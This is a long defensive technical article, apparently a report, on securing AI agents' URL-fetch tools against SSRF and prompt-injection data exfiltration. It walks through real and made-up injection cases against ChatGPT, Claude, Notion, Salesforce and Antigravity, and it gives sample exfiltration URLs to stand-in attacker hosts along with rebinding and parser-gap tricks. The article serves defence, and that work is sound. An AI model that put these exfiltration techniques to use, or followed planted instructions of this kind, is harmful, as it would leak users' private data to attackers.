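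If the check and the client run as separate programs, the check has to turn the parsed result back into text to send it to the client. Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz recommend sending the approved call in an unambiguous standard form, with a cryptographic seal to protect it from changes on the way. For a URL, that form is the address rebuilt from its checked parts.

The tool has to repeat all this for every redirect. Even if it parses each URL only once, an attacker can use DNS rebinding to change which machine the host name leads to after the check.

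### When normalization opens a gap

Normalization means rewriting equivalent forms of an address into one standard form before comparing them. Sonar's *Security Implications of URL Parsing Differentials* recommends it for gaps like those in the table, but a tool that normalizes a copy for the check and then sends the original can create a new gap.

Suppose bass.example is on the allowlist and the model passes in `https://baß.example/?code=4471`. A simple check compares the two names and refuses the request because they differ. A developer then adds a line that converts international letters using the older rules, which turn ß into "ss", so the check compares bass.example with the allowlist and approves the request. But the client receives the original URL, applies the newer rules and sends the booking code to xn--ba-hia.example, which a stranger may have registered.

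Percent-encoding can cause the same problem. If the check decodes an address before splitting it into parts, `https://docs.example%2f.attacker.example/` becomes `https://docs.example/.attacker.example/`, with docs.example as the host. A client that splits first gets one long host name ending in attacker.example. Some clients will reject that name, but others may look it up, and the attacker's name server can answer. Decoding twice creates more variants, and Tsai found libraries that did so.

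Normalizing a URL only for the check can work if the developer knows which program will read the URL next. Sonar found that an Apache login module and web browsers read backslashes differently, which let an attacker disguise the page a visitor would go to. The module's developers fixed this by turning every backslash into a forward slash before parsing, which worked because browsers make the same replacement. With a client that handles backslashes differently, the same fix could cause the check to approve the wrong host.

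Fixing one parsing disagreement often creates another. The official Go library for the Model Context Protocol, a standard that connects agents to tool servers, once ignored capitalization when matching JSON names. Its developers fixed that by switching to another decoder, but the new decoder treated certain other names as equal when they weren't, which took a further release to correct. A tool that normalizes an address, then checks and sends the normalized version, doesn't need to predict how another program will read the original.

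## What carries over from defences against server-side request forgery?

Web developers have built defences against server-side request forgery (SSRF) since at least 2014, when SafeCurl, a PHP library for safely fetching user-supplied addresses, came out. A fetch tool can reuse nearly all of these defences to protect internal machines, but only some of them also keep the customer's booking code from reaching attacker.example.

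### From link previews to the OWASP list

SSRF is a confused deputy attack, in which an attacker tricks a program into using its own authority on the attacker's behalf. Suppose the travel company's site lets visitors put a link in a review, and the company's server fetches the linked page to show a preview. A visitor who enters `http://10.0.0.5/admin` gets a preview of the company's administration page, although the firewall would block the same request from the visitor's laptop.

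Many ordinary features need requests like this, including imported calendars and webhooks (addresses that a server notifies when something happens) (Wessels, Koch and colleagues, *SSRF vs. Developers*, 2024). OWASP (2024), a non-profit that publishes guidance on web security, lists what an attacker may reach this way: other servers behind the same firewall, services on the server itself that often require no login, and tokens from a company's single sign-on system.

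In 2019, an attacker exploited an SSRF flaw at the bank Capital One and obtained credit card information on more than 100 million consumers, according to *ARTEMIS* (Ji, Dai and colleagues, 2025). UnveilTech's *SSRF defense in depth* puts the settlement at $190 million.

OWASP added SSRF to its Top 10, a widely used list of the most serious web application risks, in 2021. OWASP's *A10:2021* (2021) explains that SSRF came first in a community survey, although its average incidence in test data was relatively low, at 2.72%. OWASP hoped to merge the entry into a larger category later, and did so in the 2025 edition. SecurityWeek's *Two New Web Application Risk Categories Added to OWASP Top 10* (2025) reports that SSRF, previously tenth, is now part of Broken Access Control, which has led the list since 2021. That category covers failures to enforce who may do what. NVISO's *OWASP Top 10 2025*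 (2026) lists other flaws that lost their separate entries in the same way, so the merger doesn't mean that SSRF has become rare.

GCVE's *CWE-918* defines server-side request forgery as a server fetching a URL without sufficiently ensuring that the request goes to the "expected destination". The definition doesn't mention internal machines, which are the targets in the usual examples, so it also covers a fetch tool that approves docs.example and then contacts attacker.example. Most of the defences, however, assume that the attacker's target is inside the network.

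### Checking the text, then the address

The simplest defence compares the URL's text with a list of forbidden hosts, such as localhost and 127.0.0.1. The example program in Include Security's *Mitigating SSRF in 2023* (2023) used this check to block `http://127.0.0.1:8888/admin`, but it returned the administration page for `http://localtest.me:8888/admin`, because localtest.me is a public name whose DNS record points to 127.0.0.1. Anyone who owns a domain can create a record like that.

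A host allowlist doesn't have this weakness, since an attacker can't change the DNS records of docs.example. It stops nearly every form of SSRF, as long as the check reads the host correctly and runs again on each redirect.

The text check should also refuse every scheme except http and https. Some libraries open `file:` addresses, which point to files on the machine, and in one of the attack scenarios in OWASP's 2021 entry, an attacker reads a server's list of user accounts this way. Others support Gopher, an older protocol so simple that an attacker can use it to imitate messages in other protocols. Wessels and colleagues call this a bridging attack and warn that it can let the attacker run code on an internal server.

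To catch localtest.me, the tool has to look up the name and check the resulting address. Nette's *SSRF Protection* documents a PHP framework's validator that does this. By default, it accepts only https on port 443 and only public addresses, so it rejects private addresses, loopback addresses (which lead back to the same machine) and link-local addresses (which include the cloud metadata service).

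An address check can only block the internal addresses its developer thought of. Wessels and colleagues point out that a list of typical local addresses may leave out those a cloud provider uses internally. The check also misses a service on a public address that accepts requests only from the company's network. The service accepts the request because it comes from a server inside that network.

### DNS rebinding

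The check looks up the host, approves the address and passes the URL to the HTTP library, which then looks up the host again. In DNS rebinding, the attacker changes the answer between the two lookups. The attacker can do this because the owner of a domain controls its name server and decides how long a client may reuse an answer.

In this example, the tool may visit any public site but blocks private addresses. The address 203.0.113.9 stands for the attacker's public server.

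| Time | What happens |
|---|---|
| 0 ms | The model passes `http://r.attacker.example/admin` to the fetch tool |
| 1 ms | The check asks the DNS for the address of r.attacker.example |
| 20 ms | The attacker's name server answers 203.0.113.9 and marks the answer as valid for zero seconds |
| 21 ms | The check sees a public address and approves the URL |
| 22 ms | The HTTP library looks up the name again, because the first answer has expired |
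| 40 ms | The attacker's name server answers 10.0.0.5 |
| 41 ms | The library connects to 10.0.0.5 and sends `GET /admin` |

The URL stays the same, no server sends a redirect, and both programs read the host correctly, so checking every hop and parsing the URL only once don't help.

The repair, usually called IP pinning, is to look up the name once and connect only to the address that passed the check. It fits into the `send` step of the function that parses a URL once:

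```
function send(target):
    addresses = lookup(target.host)
    if addresses is empty or any of them is not public: refuse
    connection = connect to addresses[0] on target.port
    if target.scheme is https:
        require a valid certificate for target.host
    send GET with the header "Host: " + target.host
```

Certificate checks are easy to get wrong when pinning an address. A developer might replace the host name in the URL with 203.0.113.9. The library then checks for a certificate for 203.0.113.9, finds one for the host name and refuses the connection, as UnveilTech warns. Turning off certificate checks would remove the error but let anyone on the network path impersonate the site. The tool should give the library the address and the host name separately.

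With some clients, the developer doesn't have to look up the name separately, because the client checks the address after its own lookup. According to Wessels and colleagues, Symfony, another PHP framework, has a client that does this and blocks internal addresses.

Requiring https also weakens DNS rebinding. The internal machine at 10.0.0.5 has no valid certificate for r.attacker.example, so a client that checks certificates stops before it sends `GET /admin`. But the client has already opened a connection by then, and the attacker may learn from the type of error or the delay whether a service is running on that port.

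Pinning matters for tools that allow or block requests by network address. If a tool has a strict allowlist containing only docs.example, an attacker would need to control that site's DNS to use rebinding.

### Metadata services that require a token

An attacker who can choose only a URL can steal access tokens from a cloud's metadata service, usually at 169.254.169.254, if the service answers any plain GET request.

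Cloud providers have therefore made the request harder to forge. *SSRF Prevention*, an unsigned online guide, recommends enforcing IMDSv2, the newer version of Amazon's metadata service, and mentions that Google requires the header `Metadata-Flavor: Google`. With IMDSv2, a program obtains a session token with a PUT request and includes it in a header of each GET request. Administrators have to enforce IMDSv2 because a machine that still accepts the old version will respond to a GET request without a token.

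Azure's rule that metadata requests must carry the header `Metadata: true` failed in Copilot Studio and custom GPT Actions because the researchers could set that header in both products. IMDSv2 is stronger because the attacker must also control the request method, read the first reply and copy the token from it into another request.

A fetch tool that sends only GET requests with fixed headers can't meet any of these conditions, whatever instructions an injected comment contains. A tool that lets the model choose the method and headers could meet all of them. Developers often add these options for flexibility, but should leave them out if the agent only needs to read pages. The token rule protects only the metadata service, so the page at `http://10.0.0.5/admin` needs its own login.

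### Egress proxies and separate networks

When all outgoing requests have to pass through an egress proxy, the fetch tool sends the proxy a request to connect to a host, and the proxy allows or refuses the connection. A firewall has to block direct connections from the tool's machine, or a library that ignores the proxy settings will bypass the proxy.

The proxy closes several gaps at once:

- A redirect causes a new request, which also passes through the proxy, so the proxy checks the host at every hop.
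- The client has already parsed the URL when it names a host to the proxy. The proxy therefore judges the host that the client is really trying to reach, even if an earlier check read the URL differently.
- The proxy looks up the name and makes the connection itself, so it can use the address it has just checked.
- One set of rules covers every part of the program. Open WebUI's developers had to find the same redirect fault in five places, and a proxy that refused internal addresses would have covered all five.

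The proxy also can't inspect most of an https request. The client requests a connection to docs.example on port 443 through the proxy and then encrypts everything it sends. The proxy receives the host and port but not the path or query, so it can't enforce a path rule or search for the booking code. A company can install its own certificate so that the proxy can decrypt the traffic, but then the proxy handles every password and private page in plain text. The proxy must also compare host names correctly. Smokescreen is a proxy of this kind, and the trailing dot got past its blocklist.

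Network separation protects internal services even when every check fails. If the fetch tool runs on a machine with no route to the internal network, a request to 10.0.0.5 can't reach its target. OWASP's 2021 entry recommends separate networks along with firewall rules that deny connections by default. An attacker could still target services on the tool's own machine and, if that machine is in a cloud, the metadata service.

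Many applications have legitimate reasons to contact internal machines, which makes complete separation hard. Wessels and colleagues raise this objection to an "SSRF jail", which would block a whole program's internal connections at the operating system level. An agent that needs both the company wiki and the public web could use two tools, one on each network. But the model's context still connects them, because the agent can read a private page with the wiki tool and put what it learned into a URL for the web tool, without either machine reaching the other's network.

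Whose network is at risk also depends on where the tool runs. A tool on a user's laptop can reach the user's home router and the office network. A tool in the provider's data centre can't, but it can reach the provider's internal services, as the flaw in custom GPT Actions showed.

### How often do developers use these defences?

Wessels and colleagues analysed 27,078 PHP projects from GitHub, downloaded in July 2023. Their program traced text supplied by users to functions that can send requests, and the researchers then read the suspicious code by hand. They found 237 paths on which an attacker appeared to control the start of the address. Of these, 71 were in hacking tools and 8 in tests or examples, which left 158 in real applications:

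| Result for the 158 paths in applications | Number |
|---|---|
| Trivially exploitable | 39 |
| Needed closer study, and the attacker could choose the host | 65 |
| Needed closer study, but the attacker could not choose the host | 36 |
| False alarm | 18 |

None of the code looked up the host's address or pinned it. Four candidates turned off redirects. Only two applications had a sound defence of their own, and both used an allowlist. A separate search of 30,870 projects found only four that used an HTTP client with SSRF protection. A maintainer of one of those clients had written one of the four.

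Home-made URL checks often got details wrong. The search engine LibreX had wikimedia.org on its allowlist, but LibreX extracted the domain by splitting the address at slashes and dots and keeping the last two pieces. An address such as `http://attacker.example:22?.wikimedia.org` therefore passed, although a client would contact attacker.example.

Protection built into a platform can fail too. WordPress's documentation describes some of its request functions as safe from redirection and request forgery. Wessels and colleagues found that all but one of these functions followed a 307 redirect, and that DNS rebinding defeated the block on internal addresses. WordPress closed their rebinding report as a duplicate of one from 2017.

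Ji and colleagues built Artemis, a program that searches PHP code for SSRF flaws, and ran it on 250 applications. It found 106 flaws. Of these, 35 were new, and 24 of the new ones had received CVE numbers when the study appeared. Of the 222 paths it reported, 15 were false alarms. The best of five existing tools found 50 of the 106 flaws. One of the new flaws was in CommentLuv, a WordPress plugin that accepted any address containing "blogspot". An attacker could register a domain, create a name such as `blogspot.attacker.example` and point it at 127.0.0.1.

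These numbers don't show how common SSRF is across the web. Ji and colleagues chose 55 of their applications because they had known SSRF flaws, and both studies cover only open-source PHP code. Wessels and colleagues found potentially unsafe requests in 141 of their 27,078 projects, about 0.5%, but working defences were almost absent among those 141. An agent with a fetch tool always makes potentially unsafe requests of this kind, because the tool's purpose is to request addresses that someone else may have influenced.

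### Where the two problems differ

| | SSRF in a web application | Exfiltration through a fetch tool |
|---|---|---|
| Who writes the URL? | The attacker, usually in a form or a request | The model, which may be following text that the attacker planted |
| Where is the attacker's machine? | Anywhere; the target is a machine inside the network | On the public internet, where it receives the request, unless the attacker collects the data through an approved site |
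| Is the harm in the request or the reply? | Often in the reply, which contains internal data; sometimes in the request, if it changes something | In the request, which carries the private data |
| Can the developer close off the public web? | Often, if the application needs only a few known services; not if it previews any link | Yes for an assistant with a narrow task; no for an agent that browses the web |

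A standard SSRF defence can leave the booking code unprotected. Nette's default policy would approve `https://attacker.example/log?code=4471`, because the scheme is https, the port is 443 and the host has a public address. Pinning would then make sure that the tool connects to the attacker's server. Cutting the machine off from the metadata service and the rest of the internal network wouldn't prevent this, because the request only needs access to the internet.

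The defences that carry over ensure that a rule, whatever it is, applies to the request that is actually sent. Checking every hop and parsing the URL once work equally well with a block on private addresses, a host allowlist or an exact-address match. An egress proxy can enforce the block and the host allowlist, but it can enforce an exact-address match on https requests only if it decrypts them. To protect the booking code, the developer needs a host allowlist or an exact-address match.

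A web application can reduce the harm from SSRF by not showing the fetched reply to the visitor, for example by displaying only a page's title. This defence loses most of its value in an agent, because the fetch tool has to give the model enough of the reply to answer the user's question, and the model may then leak it.

The model also makes it harder to find flaws in the code. Artemis follows user input from the form where it arrives to the function that sends the request. In an agent, that path runs through the model, and programs like Artemis can't trace a URL back to the sentence in the context that led the model to write it. The safe assumption is that an attacker may have written any URL the model produces.

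### An experiment with a ticket assistant

Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian (2026), in *From Prompt Injection to Web Exploitation*, tested how easily an attacker can carry out SSRF through a model's tool calls. They built TicketOracle, a small web application with an assistant that answers questions about concerts. The assistant's only tool sent a GET request to any URL and returned the start of the reply. An administration service on the same machine required no login and accepted only local connections, so the assistant's tool could reach it but an outsider couldn't connect directly.

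The researchers tried five attacks in April 2026. In four of them, the attacker typed instructions straight into the chat:

- **Port probe:** the assistant requests an address on its own machine, and the attacker learns from the answer whether a service is running there.
- **Data leak:** the assistant fetches the list of users, including phone numbers and addresses.
- **Deletion:** the assistant opens an address that deletes a user and reports the result.
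- **Blind deletion:** the assistant does the same, but the reply is empty, so only the server's log shows whether the request went out.

In the fifth attack, the attacker planted instructions in a concert review. An innocent user then asked about the concert, and the assistant read the review.

The researchers ran the assistant with and without an allowlist. The allowlist was a set of permitted URL patterns written into the model's system prompt, along with an instruction to refuse all others. No code enforced it. Each model faced each attack ten times:

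| Model | Port probe | Data leak | Deletion | Blind deletion | Planted review, no allowlist | Planted review, allowlist in prompt |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Llama 3.3 70B | 10 | 10 | 10 | 10 | 6 | 10 |
| Qwen3 Coder 480B | 9 | 10 | 10 | 7 | 0 | 0 |
| DeepSeek R1 | 10 | 10 | 10 | 7 | 0 | 0 |
| GPT-oss 120B | 3 | 0 | 10 | 0 | 5 | 0 |
| Gemini 3 Pro Preview | 0 | 7 | 10 | 0 | 0 | 0 |
| GPT-5.2 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 |
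| Claude Opus 4.6 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 |

The table shows the four direct attacks without the allowlist. With it, all four failed against every model, but the planted review still succeeded in all ten trials against Llama 3.3. The review included a claim that the allowlist now contained the administration address, and the model accepted this claim.

The evidence is thin for Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian's conclusion that the allowlist made the attack on Llama more effective. Successes rose from six to ten in ten trials, but Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian had also added the false claim about the allowlist to the review for the test with the allowlist, so the attack changed along with the defence. The rise could also be chance. The trials weren't independent, because all ten took place in one conversation. Claude's refusals, for example, grew shorter as the same request was repeated.

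For developers, the more important result is that the attack succeeded in all ten trials. The model interpreted both the allowlist in the prompt and the planted review as text. Code that compares the host with an allowlist would have refused 127.0.0.1 every time, regardless of the review's content.

The zeros for GPT-5.2 and Claude Opus 4.6 are encouraging but don't show that these models are safe to use without a check. The attacks were simple and not tuned to any model. The count may also miss some requests because, except in the blind attack, a trial counted as a success only if the assistant both sent the request and repeated the result to the user. If a model had deleted a user without mentioning it, the trial would have counted as a failed attack.

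Gemini and GPT-oss refused the blind deletion every time but carried out the ordinary deletion every time, although both requests had the same effect on the database. This inconsistency is another reason not to rely on a model's refusals, since a check in code would handle both requests the same way.

Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian recommend that the model not supply the URL. A ticket assistant only needs to choose a concert, so the model can return the concert's identifier and ordinary code can check it and build the URL. The travel assistant could choose a help page from a fixed list in the same way. An injected comment could then make it open the wrong page on docs.example, but could not add the booking code to the URL or send the request anywhere else. They also recommend that administration pages require a login even for requests from the same machine, which would have protected TicketOracle's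 users with every model tested.

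## Which URL checks hold, and what do they cost?

A ticket assistant can choose pages from a fixed list, but a general-purpose agent has to open addresses its developer never listed. OpenAI and Anthropic give such agents checks that depend on where an address came from, not on who owns the host. These checks keep the model from writing a secret, such as a booking code, into a URL. They also block some harmless pages, and an attacker can still get a short secret past them by making the agent choose among approved addresses.

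### Addresses that are already public

ChatGPT's early check approved whole sites, and Tenable (2025) got past it with Bing's tracking links. OpenAI later limited ChatGPT to opening URLs exactly as it received them, with no added parameters, according to *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack*. This blocked ShadowLeak, an attack in which the model itself added private data to an address. Researchers at the security company Radware then rewrote the injection to include a complete list of ready-made addresses, each ending in a different letter or digit, so the model could spell out the data by opening addresses from the list.

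The exact-address match that OpenAI described in January 2026 requires an independent crawler to have already recorded each address, a condition that a list like Radware's may not meet. The crawler discovers public pages as a search engine does and has no access to users' conversations, accounts or personal data. If it hasn't recorded an address, the agent has to try another site or the user gets a warning.

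This check works only if the crawler is independent of conversations. If its records also included addresses from conversations, the model could write the code into a new address, and the check might later find that address on record.

OpenAI doesn't rely on a list of trusted sites because it would produce too many warnings and because many legitimate sites redirect visitors elsewhere. The second reason is weaker than it looks, since a tool that checks every hop would catch the redirect. Shared hosts are a better reason, because an attacker on a trusted shared host needs no redirect. Requiring an exact match with an address the crawler has already seen stops those leaks too, because the crawler has never seen an address containing that customer's data.

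The only guarantee the company claims for the rule is that the agent won't quietly leak user-specific data through the URL itself. A page that passes may still contain injected instructions. OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) reports that most of the attacks it knows of fail earlier, because training leads the model to refuse. For the rest, Safe Url either shows the user the information that would be sent and asks for confirmation, or blocks the request. OpenAI applies it to page visits and bookmarks in Atlas, its browser, and to searches and page visits in Deep Research, ChatGPT's feature for long research tasks.

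One outside test fits this account but doesn't confirm it. *The Framing Gap* reports that attacks that succeeded in up to 100% of trials against a model accessed through its API failed in all 48 valid trials against the ChatGPT product. The researchers couldn't see inside the product, so they didn't attribute the result to any particular defence.

### Addresses from the user or a search

Few developers can run a crawler of the whole web. Anthropic's rule for Claude's fetch tool, web_fetch, is much easier to copy. The tool may open only exact addresses that the user has entered or that Claude's own search tool has returned, as Willison (2026), in *How I tricked Claude into leaking your deepest, darkest secrets*, explains. In outline:

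```
seen = empty set
when the user sends a message: add its addresses to seen
when the search tool returns results: add their addresses to seen

function may_fetch(url):
    return url is in seen
```

This refuses `https://attacker.example/log?code=4471` because neither the customer nor the search tool supplied that address.

The rule used to allow a third source, pages that web_fetch had already fetched, and Ayush Paul found a way to exploit this. His page claimed to be protecting a website from abuse and told AI assistants to identify themselves by finding their user's profile, one letter at a time. Each page contained links for the next letter. The site showed these instructions only to clients that identified themselves as Claude's fetch tool, so a person who opened the page was less likely to notice anything odd. Claude followed the links and revealed the user's name, home city and employer,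 which it knew from earlier conversations.

The same trick works on the booking code. A page on attacker.example links to ten addresses, from `/0` to `/9`. The page at `/4` links to `/40` through `/49`, and the next two pages continue in the same way. The fourth link the model opens is `/4471`, which contains the whole code, although the model has only opened links that appeared on a page. The attacker doesn't have to store the site's 11,110 pages, because the server can generate each one on request.

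Anthropic told Paul that it had already found the problem internally, and paid no bounty. It fixed the problem by stopping web_fetch from following links in the pages it fetches. Hackaday's *This Week In Security* describes the attack as prevented "for now". The fix also limits ordinary browsing, which relies on following links. Claude can still open a table of contents, but it can't open a chapter unless a search returns the chapter's address or the user supplies it.

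A developer who copies the rule should be careful about what counts as the user's own input. If a customer pastes an email into the chat and the software approves every URL in it, the email's sender has chosen some of the approved URLs. Radware's list of ready-made links would then pass the check.

The search tool has to be safe as well as the fetch tool. In September 2025 Willison described Abi Raghuram's attack on Notion's AI agent. Raghuram hid instructions in a PDF, as white text on a white background, for the agent to gather a company's client names and revenue figures, put them into a URL and submit it as a web search. The search tool accepted URLs as well as search terms, so the data went to the attacker's server. Even a perfect check on the fetch tool would not have prevented this. A search tool should treat a URL as ordinary search text and never open it.

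### Spelling with approved addresses

Johann Rehberger, who writes the blog Embrace The Red, considers OpenAI's rule a significant improvement but says an attacker can still spell out a secret with public addresses. Anyone with a fairly large website probably already has 36 pages in the crawler's records, enough to assign one to each letter and digit. Rehberger described the method in 2023 and says that OpenAI acknowledges it in the accompanying paper.

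He adds that an attacker could extend the vocabulary to thousands of pages. The table shows how few requests would then be needed if the attacker controls all the pages, the requests arrive in order, and the model follows the most efficient code possible.

| Approved pages the attacker controls | Requests for a four-digit code | Requests for a random key of 20 letters and digits |
|---|---|---|
| 36 | 3 | 24 |
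| 1,000 | 2 | 12 |
| 10,000 | 1 | 9 |

In the last row, the attacker publishes a page for every possible booking code and waits for the crawler to record them. `https://attacker.example/log/4471` is then a public address and passes the check. An exact match protects a secret only if the attacker can't list the possible values in advance, so it works much better for passwords and documents than for four-digit codes or answers to yes-or-no questions.

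Models make mistakes with long instructions of this kind, which offers a little protection. Lan and colleagues tested a small model on an injection that told it to split a secret into four pieces and send each separately. The attack's success rate was 17 to 37 percentage points lower than when the secret was sent in one request, depending on where the instruction appeared on the page. Claude's success with Paul's letter-by-letter site suggests that stronger models are better at such tasks.

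Rehberger proposes that the agent never request the same full address twice in a session. It would either refuse the second request or answer it from a stored copy of the first reply. If an attacker sets up ten pages, one per digit, an agent leaking the code 4471 would then open only the pages for 4, 7 and 1. An attacker who knows that the code has four digits would be left with six possibilities: 4471, 4741, 4714, 4771, 4717 and 4711. The attacker can get around the rule by using a separate set of ten pages for each position, as with the Hugging Face download counts. Rehberger expects the rule only to limit such leaks.

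He also worries that some OpenAI teams may not know about the mitigation and may ship a feature without it, as happened with an earlier check.

### Six addresses, five checks

The strengths of the different checks are easier to compare on the same requests. Suppose the travel assistant's allowlist contains only docs.example, and the model passes one of these addresses to the fetch tool:

- **Approved page:** `https://docs.example/guides/baggage`
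- **Open redirect:** `https://docs.example/out?to=https://attacker.example/log?code=4471`
- **Lookalike host:** `https://docs.example.attacker.example/log?code=4471`
- **Short link:** `https://short.example/x7Kq2b`, which leads to a page on attacker.example
- **Shared host:** `https://docs.example/mallory/notes?code=4471`
- **New page:** `https://docs.example/guides/strollers`, which the travel company published an hour ago

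The prefix test approves any URL that begins with `https://docs.example`, a prefix with no final slash. The crawler has recorded only the baggage guide, the short link and the page the short link leads to. The tool parses each URL once and requests the same parsed URL it checked, so parsing gaps have no effect here.

| Address | Prefix test | Exact host, first hop | Exact host, every hop | Exact public address, first hop | Exact public address, every hop |
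|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Approved page | Opens | Opens | Opens | Opens | Opens |
| Open redirect | **Leaks** | **Leaks** | Stops before attacker.example | Refuses | Refuses |
| Lookalike host | **Leaks** | Refuses | Refuses | Refuses | Refuses |
| Short link | Refuses | Refuses | Refuses | Opens the attacker's page | Opens the attacker's page |
| Shared host | **Leaks** | **Leaks** | **Leaks** | Refuses | Refuses |
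| New page | Opens | Opens | Opens | Refuses or warns | Refuses or warns |

The entries are reasoning from how each check works, not measurements. "Leaks" means that the booking code reaches an outsider.

The exact match is the only check that stops every leak in the table, but it is also the only one that refuses the new page. It opens the short link, which the host checks refuse. No code leaks that way, but the model reads a page that a stranger wrote and that may contain more instructions. If the stranger has changed the short link's destination since the crawler's visit, a check on every hop will refuse the new destination unless the crawler has recorded that address too.

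Combining the checks helps only if an address has to pass both. An assistant that requires an approved host and a public address would refuse the short link, all three leaks and the new page. An assistant that requires only one of the two would open the new page, but the leak through the shared host would return.

It is unclear from OpenAI's post which of the last two columns describes ChatGPT. The post cites redirects as a weakness of site lists but doesn't specify whether ChatGPT also looks up the second address when a public one redirects. The companion paper, *Preventing URL-Based Data Exfiltration in Language-Model Agents*, covers the rule in more detail, but Rehberger's summary of the paper does not cover redirects.

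For a plain fetch tool, the missing detail matters little to the booking code, because a server can't pass on a code it never received. It could matter a lot in a browser where the user is logged in. Suppose the login page of docs.example redirects customers to any address named in the link and adds a sign-in token to that address, as badly configured login systems can. An attacker publishes a login link that names attacker.example, and the crawler records it. The link contains nothing private, so the check approves it. The browser sends the customer's cookie, docs.example recognises the customer, and the redirect carries the token to attacker.example. Requiring a match on every hop would stop this, since the crawler can't have seen an address with that customer's token.

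Requiring a match on every hop also blocks redirects to internal machines, because a public crawler can't reach their pages. But it would refuse many ordinary redirects too, since they end at an address that the site creates for one visit. A tool that sends no cookies can reasonably match only the first address exactly and block private addresses on every hop. A logged-in browser needs either a match on every hop or a warning before it leaves the site.

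The results in the two host columns also depend on someone keeping the allowlist up to date. Willison describes ForcedLeak, an attack on Salesforce's AI agent that exploited an outdated allowlist. Salesforce's security policy let the agent's web page load images from a domain the company had once used, but whose registration had expired. Researchers bought the domain and planted instructions in a contact form that feeds sales enquiries to the agent. The agent then displayed an image from the domain with customers' email addresses in the URL, and the researchers read the addresses in their server log. Salesforce corrected its list and added a mechanism to stop the agent from producing links to untrusted domains.

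Google's coding tool Antigravity had a worse entry on its default allowlist, webhook.site, which lets anyone create an address and watch the requests that arrive there. PromptArmor showed that an injected web page could use it to collect a programmer's cloud credentials. An exact host check would have approved both domains on every hop, but an exact public match would have refused the addresses because they contained data that no crawler had seen.

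### What the Silent Egress tests measured

Lan and colleagues ran one of the few experiments that put several defences in front of the same model and the same attack. They ran each defence 30 times with qwen2.5:7b and a malicious page that told the model to send a secret from its context to an outside server:

| Defence | Model tried to send the secret | Secret got out |
|---|---|---|
| None | 100% | 100% |
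| Prompt that forbids following instructions from web pages | 66.7% | 66.7% |
| Tags that mark web content as untrusted | 100% | 100% |
| Prompt and tags together | 56.7% | 56.7% |
| Host allowlist | 100% | 0% |
| "Redirect detection" | 83.3% | 0% |
| Filter for words such as "secret" and "token" | 23.3% | 0% |
| Filter for random-looking values | 0% | 0% |
| All of the above | 0% | 0% |

The hardened prompt still failed in 20 of 30 runs. Adding the tags reduced this to 17, a difference small enough to be chance. The model made an attempt in every run with the allowlist, and the allowlist stopped them all, which is strong evidence that developers should enforce the rule in code. Comparing host names gives the same answer every time, so this allowlist would refuse the host in any number of runs, even though zero leaks in 30 runs would normally be compatible with a true rate of up to about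 10%.

Lan and colleagues tested only an attacker host that was plainly outside the policy. The attacker's server was at evil-collector.net, and the allowlist held four hosts, three belonging to an imaginary company plus example.com. The test therefore corresponds to an ordinary request to attacker.example. It included no open redirect and no shared host, the two cases in which an exact host check on the first hop fails. Lan and colleagues acknowledge that attackers could route data through open redirects or compromised legitimate sites.

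"Redirect detection" followed no redirects. It seems to have stopped the attack because the filter refused any path containing "collect" and the researchers had named theirs `/collect`, so the zero in the table seems to depend on that name. The attack's host had a `.net` name, which was not among the blocked endings, and an attacker who chose `/guides` instead would have passed. This test therefore can't support the description of "redirect-chain analysis" in the paper's abstract as one of the more effective defences.

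The results for the two content filters are also hard to interpret. The filters ran when the tool executed a request, so they should not have affected what the model tried to send. Yet it tried to send the secret in every run without a defence, in 23.3% of runs with one filter, and in none with the other. Lan and colleagues suggest that the model avoids random-looking values under such monitoring. An unreported difference between the test conditions seems at least as likely an explanation.

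A more basic limit is that the filter for random-looking values cannot block any value with fewer than 17 different characters. It blocks values of more than 10 characters whose Shannon entropy, a measure of how varied the characters are, is above 4 bits per character, and a text with *k* different characters can score at most log₂ *k*. The paper's example key, `SECRET_API_KEY_12345`, has 16 different characters and scores about 3.85, so the filter would have let it through. A four-digit booking code is too short for the filter to examine at all.

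All these rates come from one small model, with the secret placed directly in its context and almost no safety instructions. Newer models resist much better. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports an evaluation of 72 injection scenarios that Anthropic commissioned from Trajectory Labs. The attacks succeeded in 0.09% of attempts on average against Anthropic's latest models with permission checks switched off, and in 19.03% against OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol with full access. Trajectory Labs used its own browser tools, without the safeguards that either company builds into its browser products. The gap between the models is a good reason to keep the URL check in code, since a developer may later switch to a less resistant model.

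### Broken links and delay

A host allowlist causes few problems for the travel assistant, because its developer knows which site it needs. The same list would make a general research agent nearly useless, so such an agent needs a rule like OpenAI's or Anthropic's. Those rules fail on different pages:

| Page | Public-address rule | Address from the user or a search |
|---|---|---|
| A guide published an hour ago | Fails until the crawler has seen it | Works if the user supplies the link |
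| A customer's own order page | Usually fails | Works if the user supplies the link |
| Results of a search form on a site | Usually fails | Fails unless someone has supplied that exact address |
| The next chapter of an online manual | Works if the crawler has seen it | Fails unless a search finds it |

The results in this table are also inferred. OpenAI doesn't say how often ordinary links fail its match, and there is no comparable figure for Claude's rule, so we can't tell which breaks more pages. ChatGPT also appears to accept addresses the user typed, which would let the first two rows pass.

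Small differences in an address can also make an exact match fail. For example, a newsletter may add `?source=june` to a link that the crawler recorded without it. If the tool ignores the extra part when comparing, it will send an address the check has not approved, and the ignored part could contain a booking code. The tool can safely look for the shorter address in the records and, if it is there, request that recorded address. Some links need their parameters and will open the wrong page, but nothing the model has added will leave the machine.

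The checks should add little delay, because looking up an address in a set is fast compared with fetching a page. Checking every hop repeats that lookup for each redirect. A tool that reports redirects to the model is slower, since the model has to run again before the next request. Answering repeated requests from a stored copy, as Rehberger suggests, would save time. Asking a person takes by far the longest, and an agent that works overnight may wait until morning.

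Willison reported in June 2026 that OpenAI was introducing Lockdown Mode, a much stricter setting that limits ChatGPT's outgoing requests so that an injection can't complete the theft of data. ChatGPT may still read injected instructions in stored copies of web pages or in uploaded files. OpenAI's head of security said the mode was not meant for everyone and involved some loss of function. Willison praised it for relying on fixed rules that no AI system has to interpret, but he also took its existence as a sign that ChatGPT's default settings don't protect against a determined attacker.

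### Warnings that people click through

When an automatic check can't approve an address, the tool can ask the user. Anthropic reports that users of its coding agent, Claude Code, approve 97% of such prompts, though these concern commands, not links. Most of those commands are probably harmless, so the figure alone doesn't show that users are careless.

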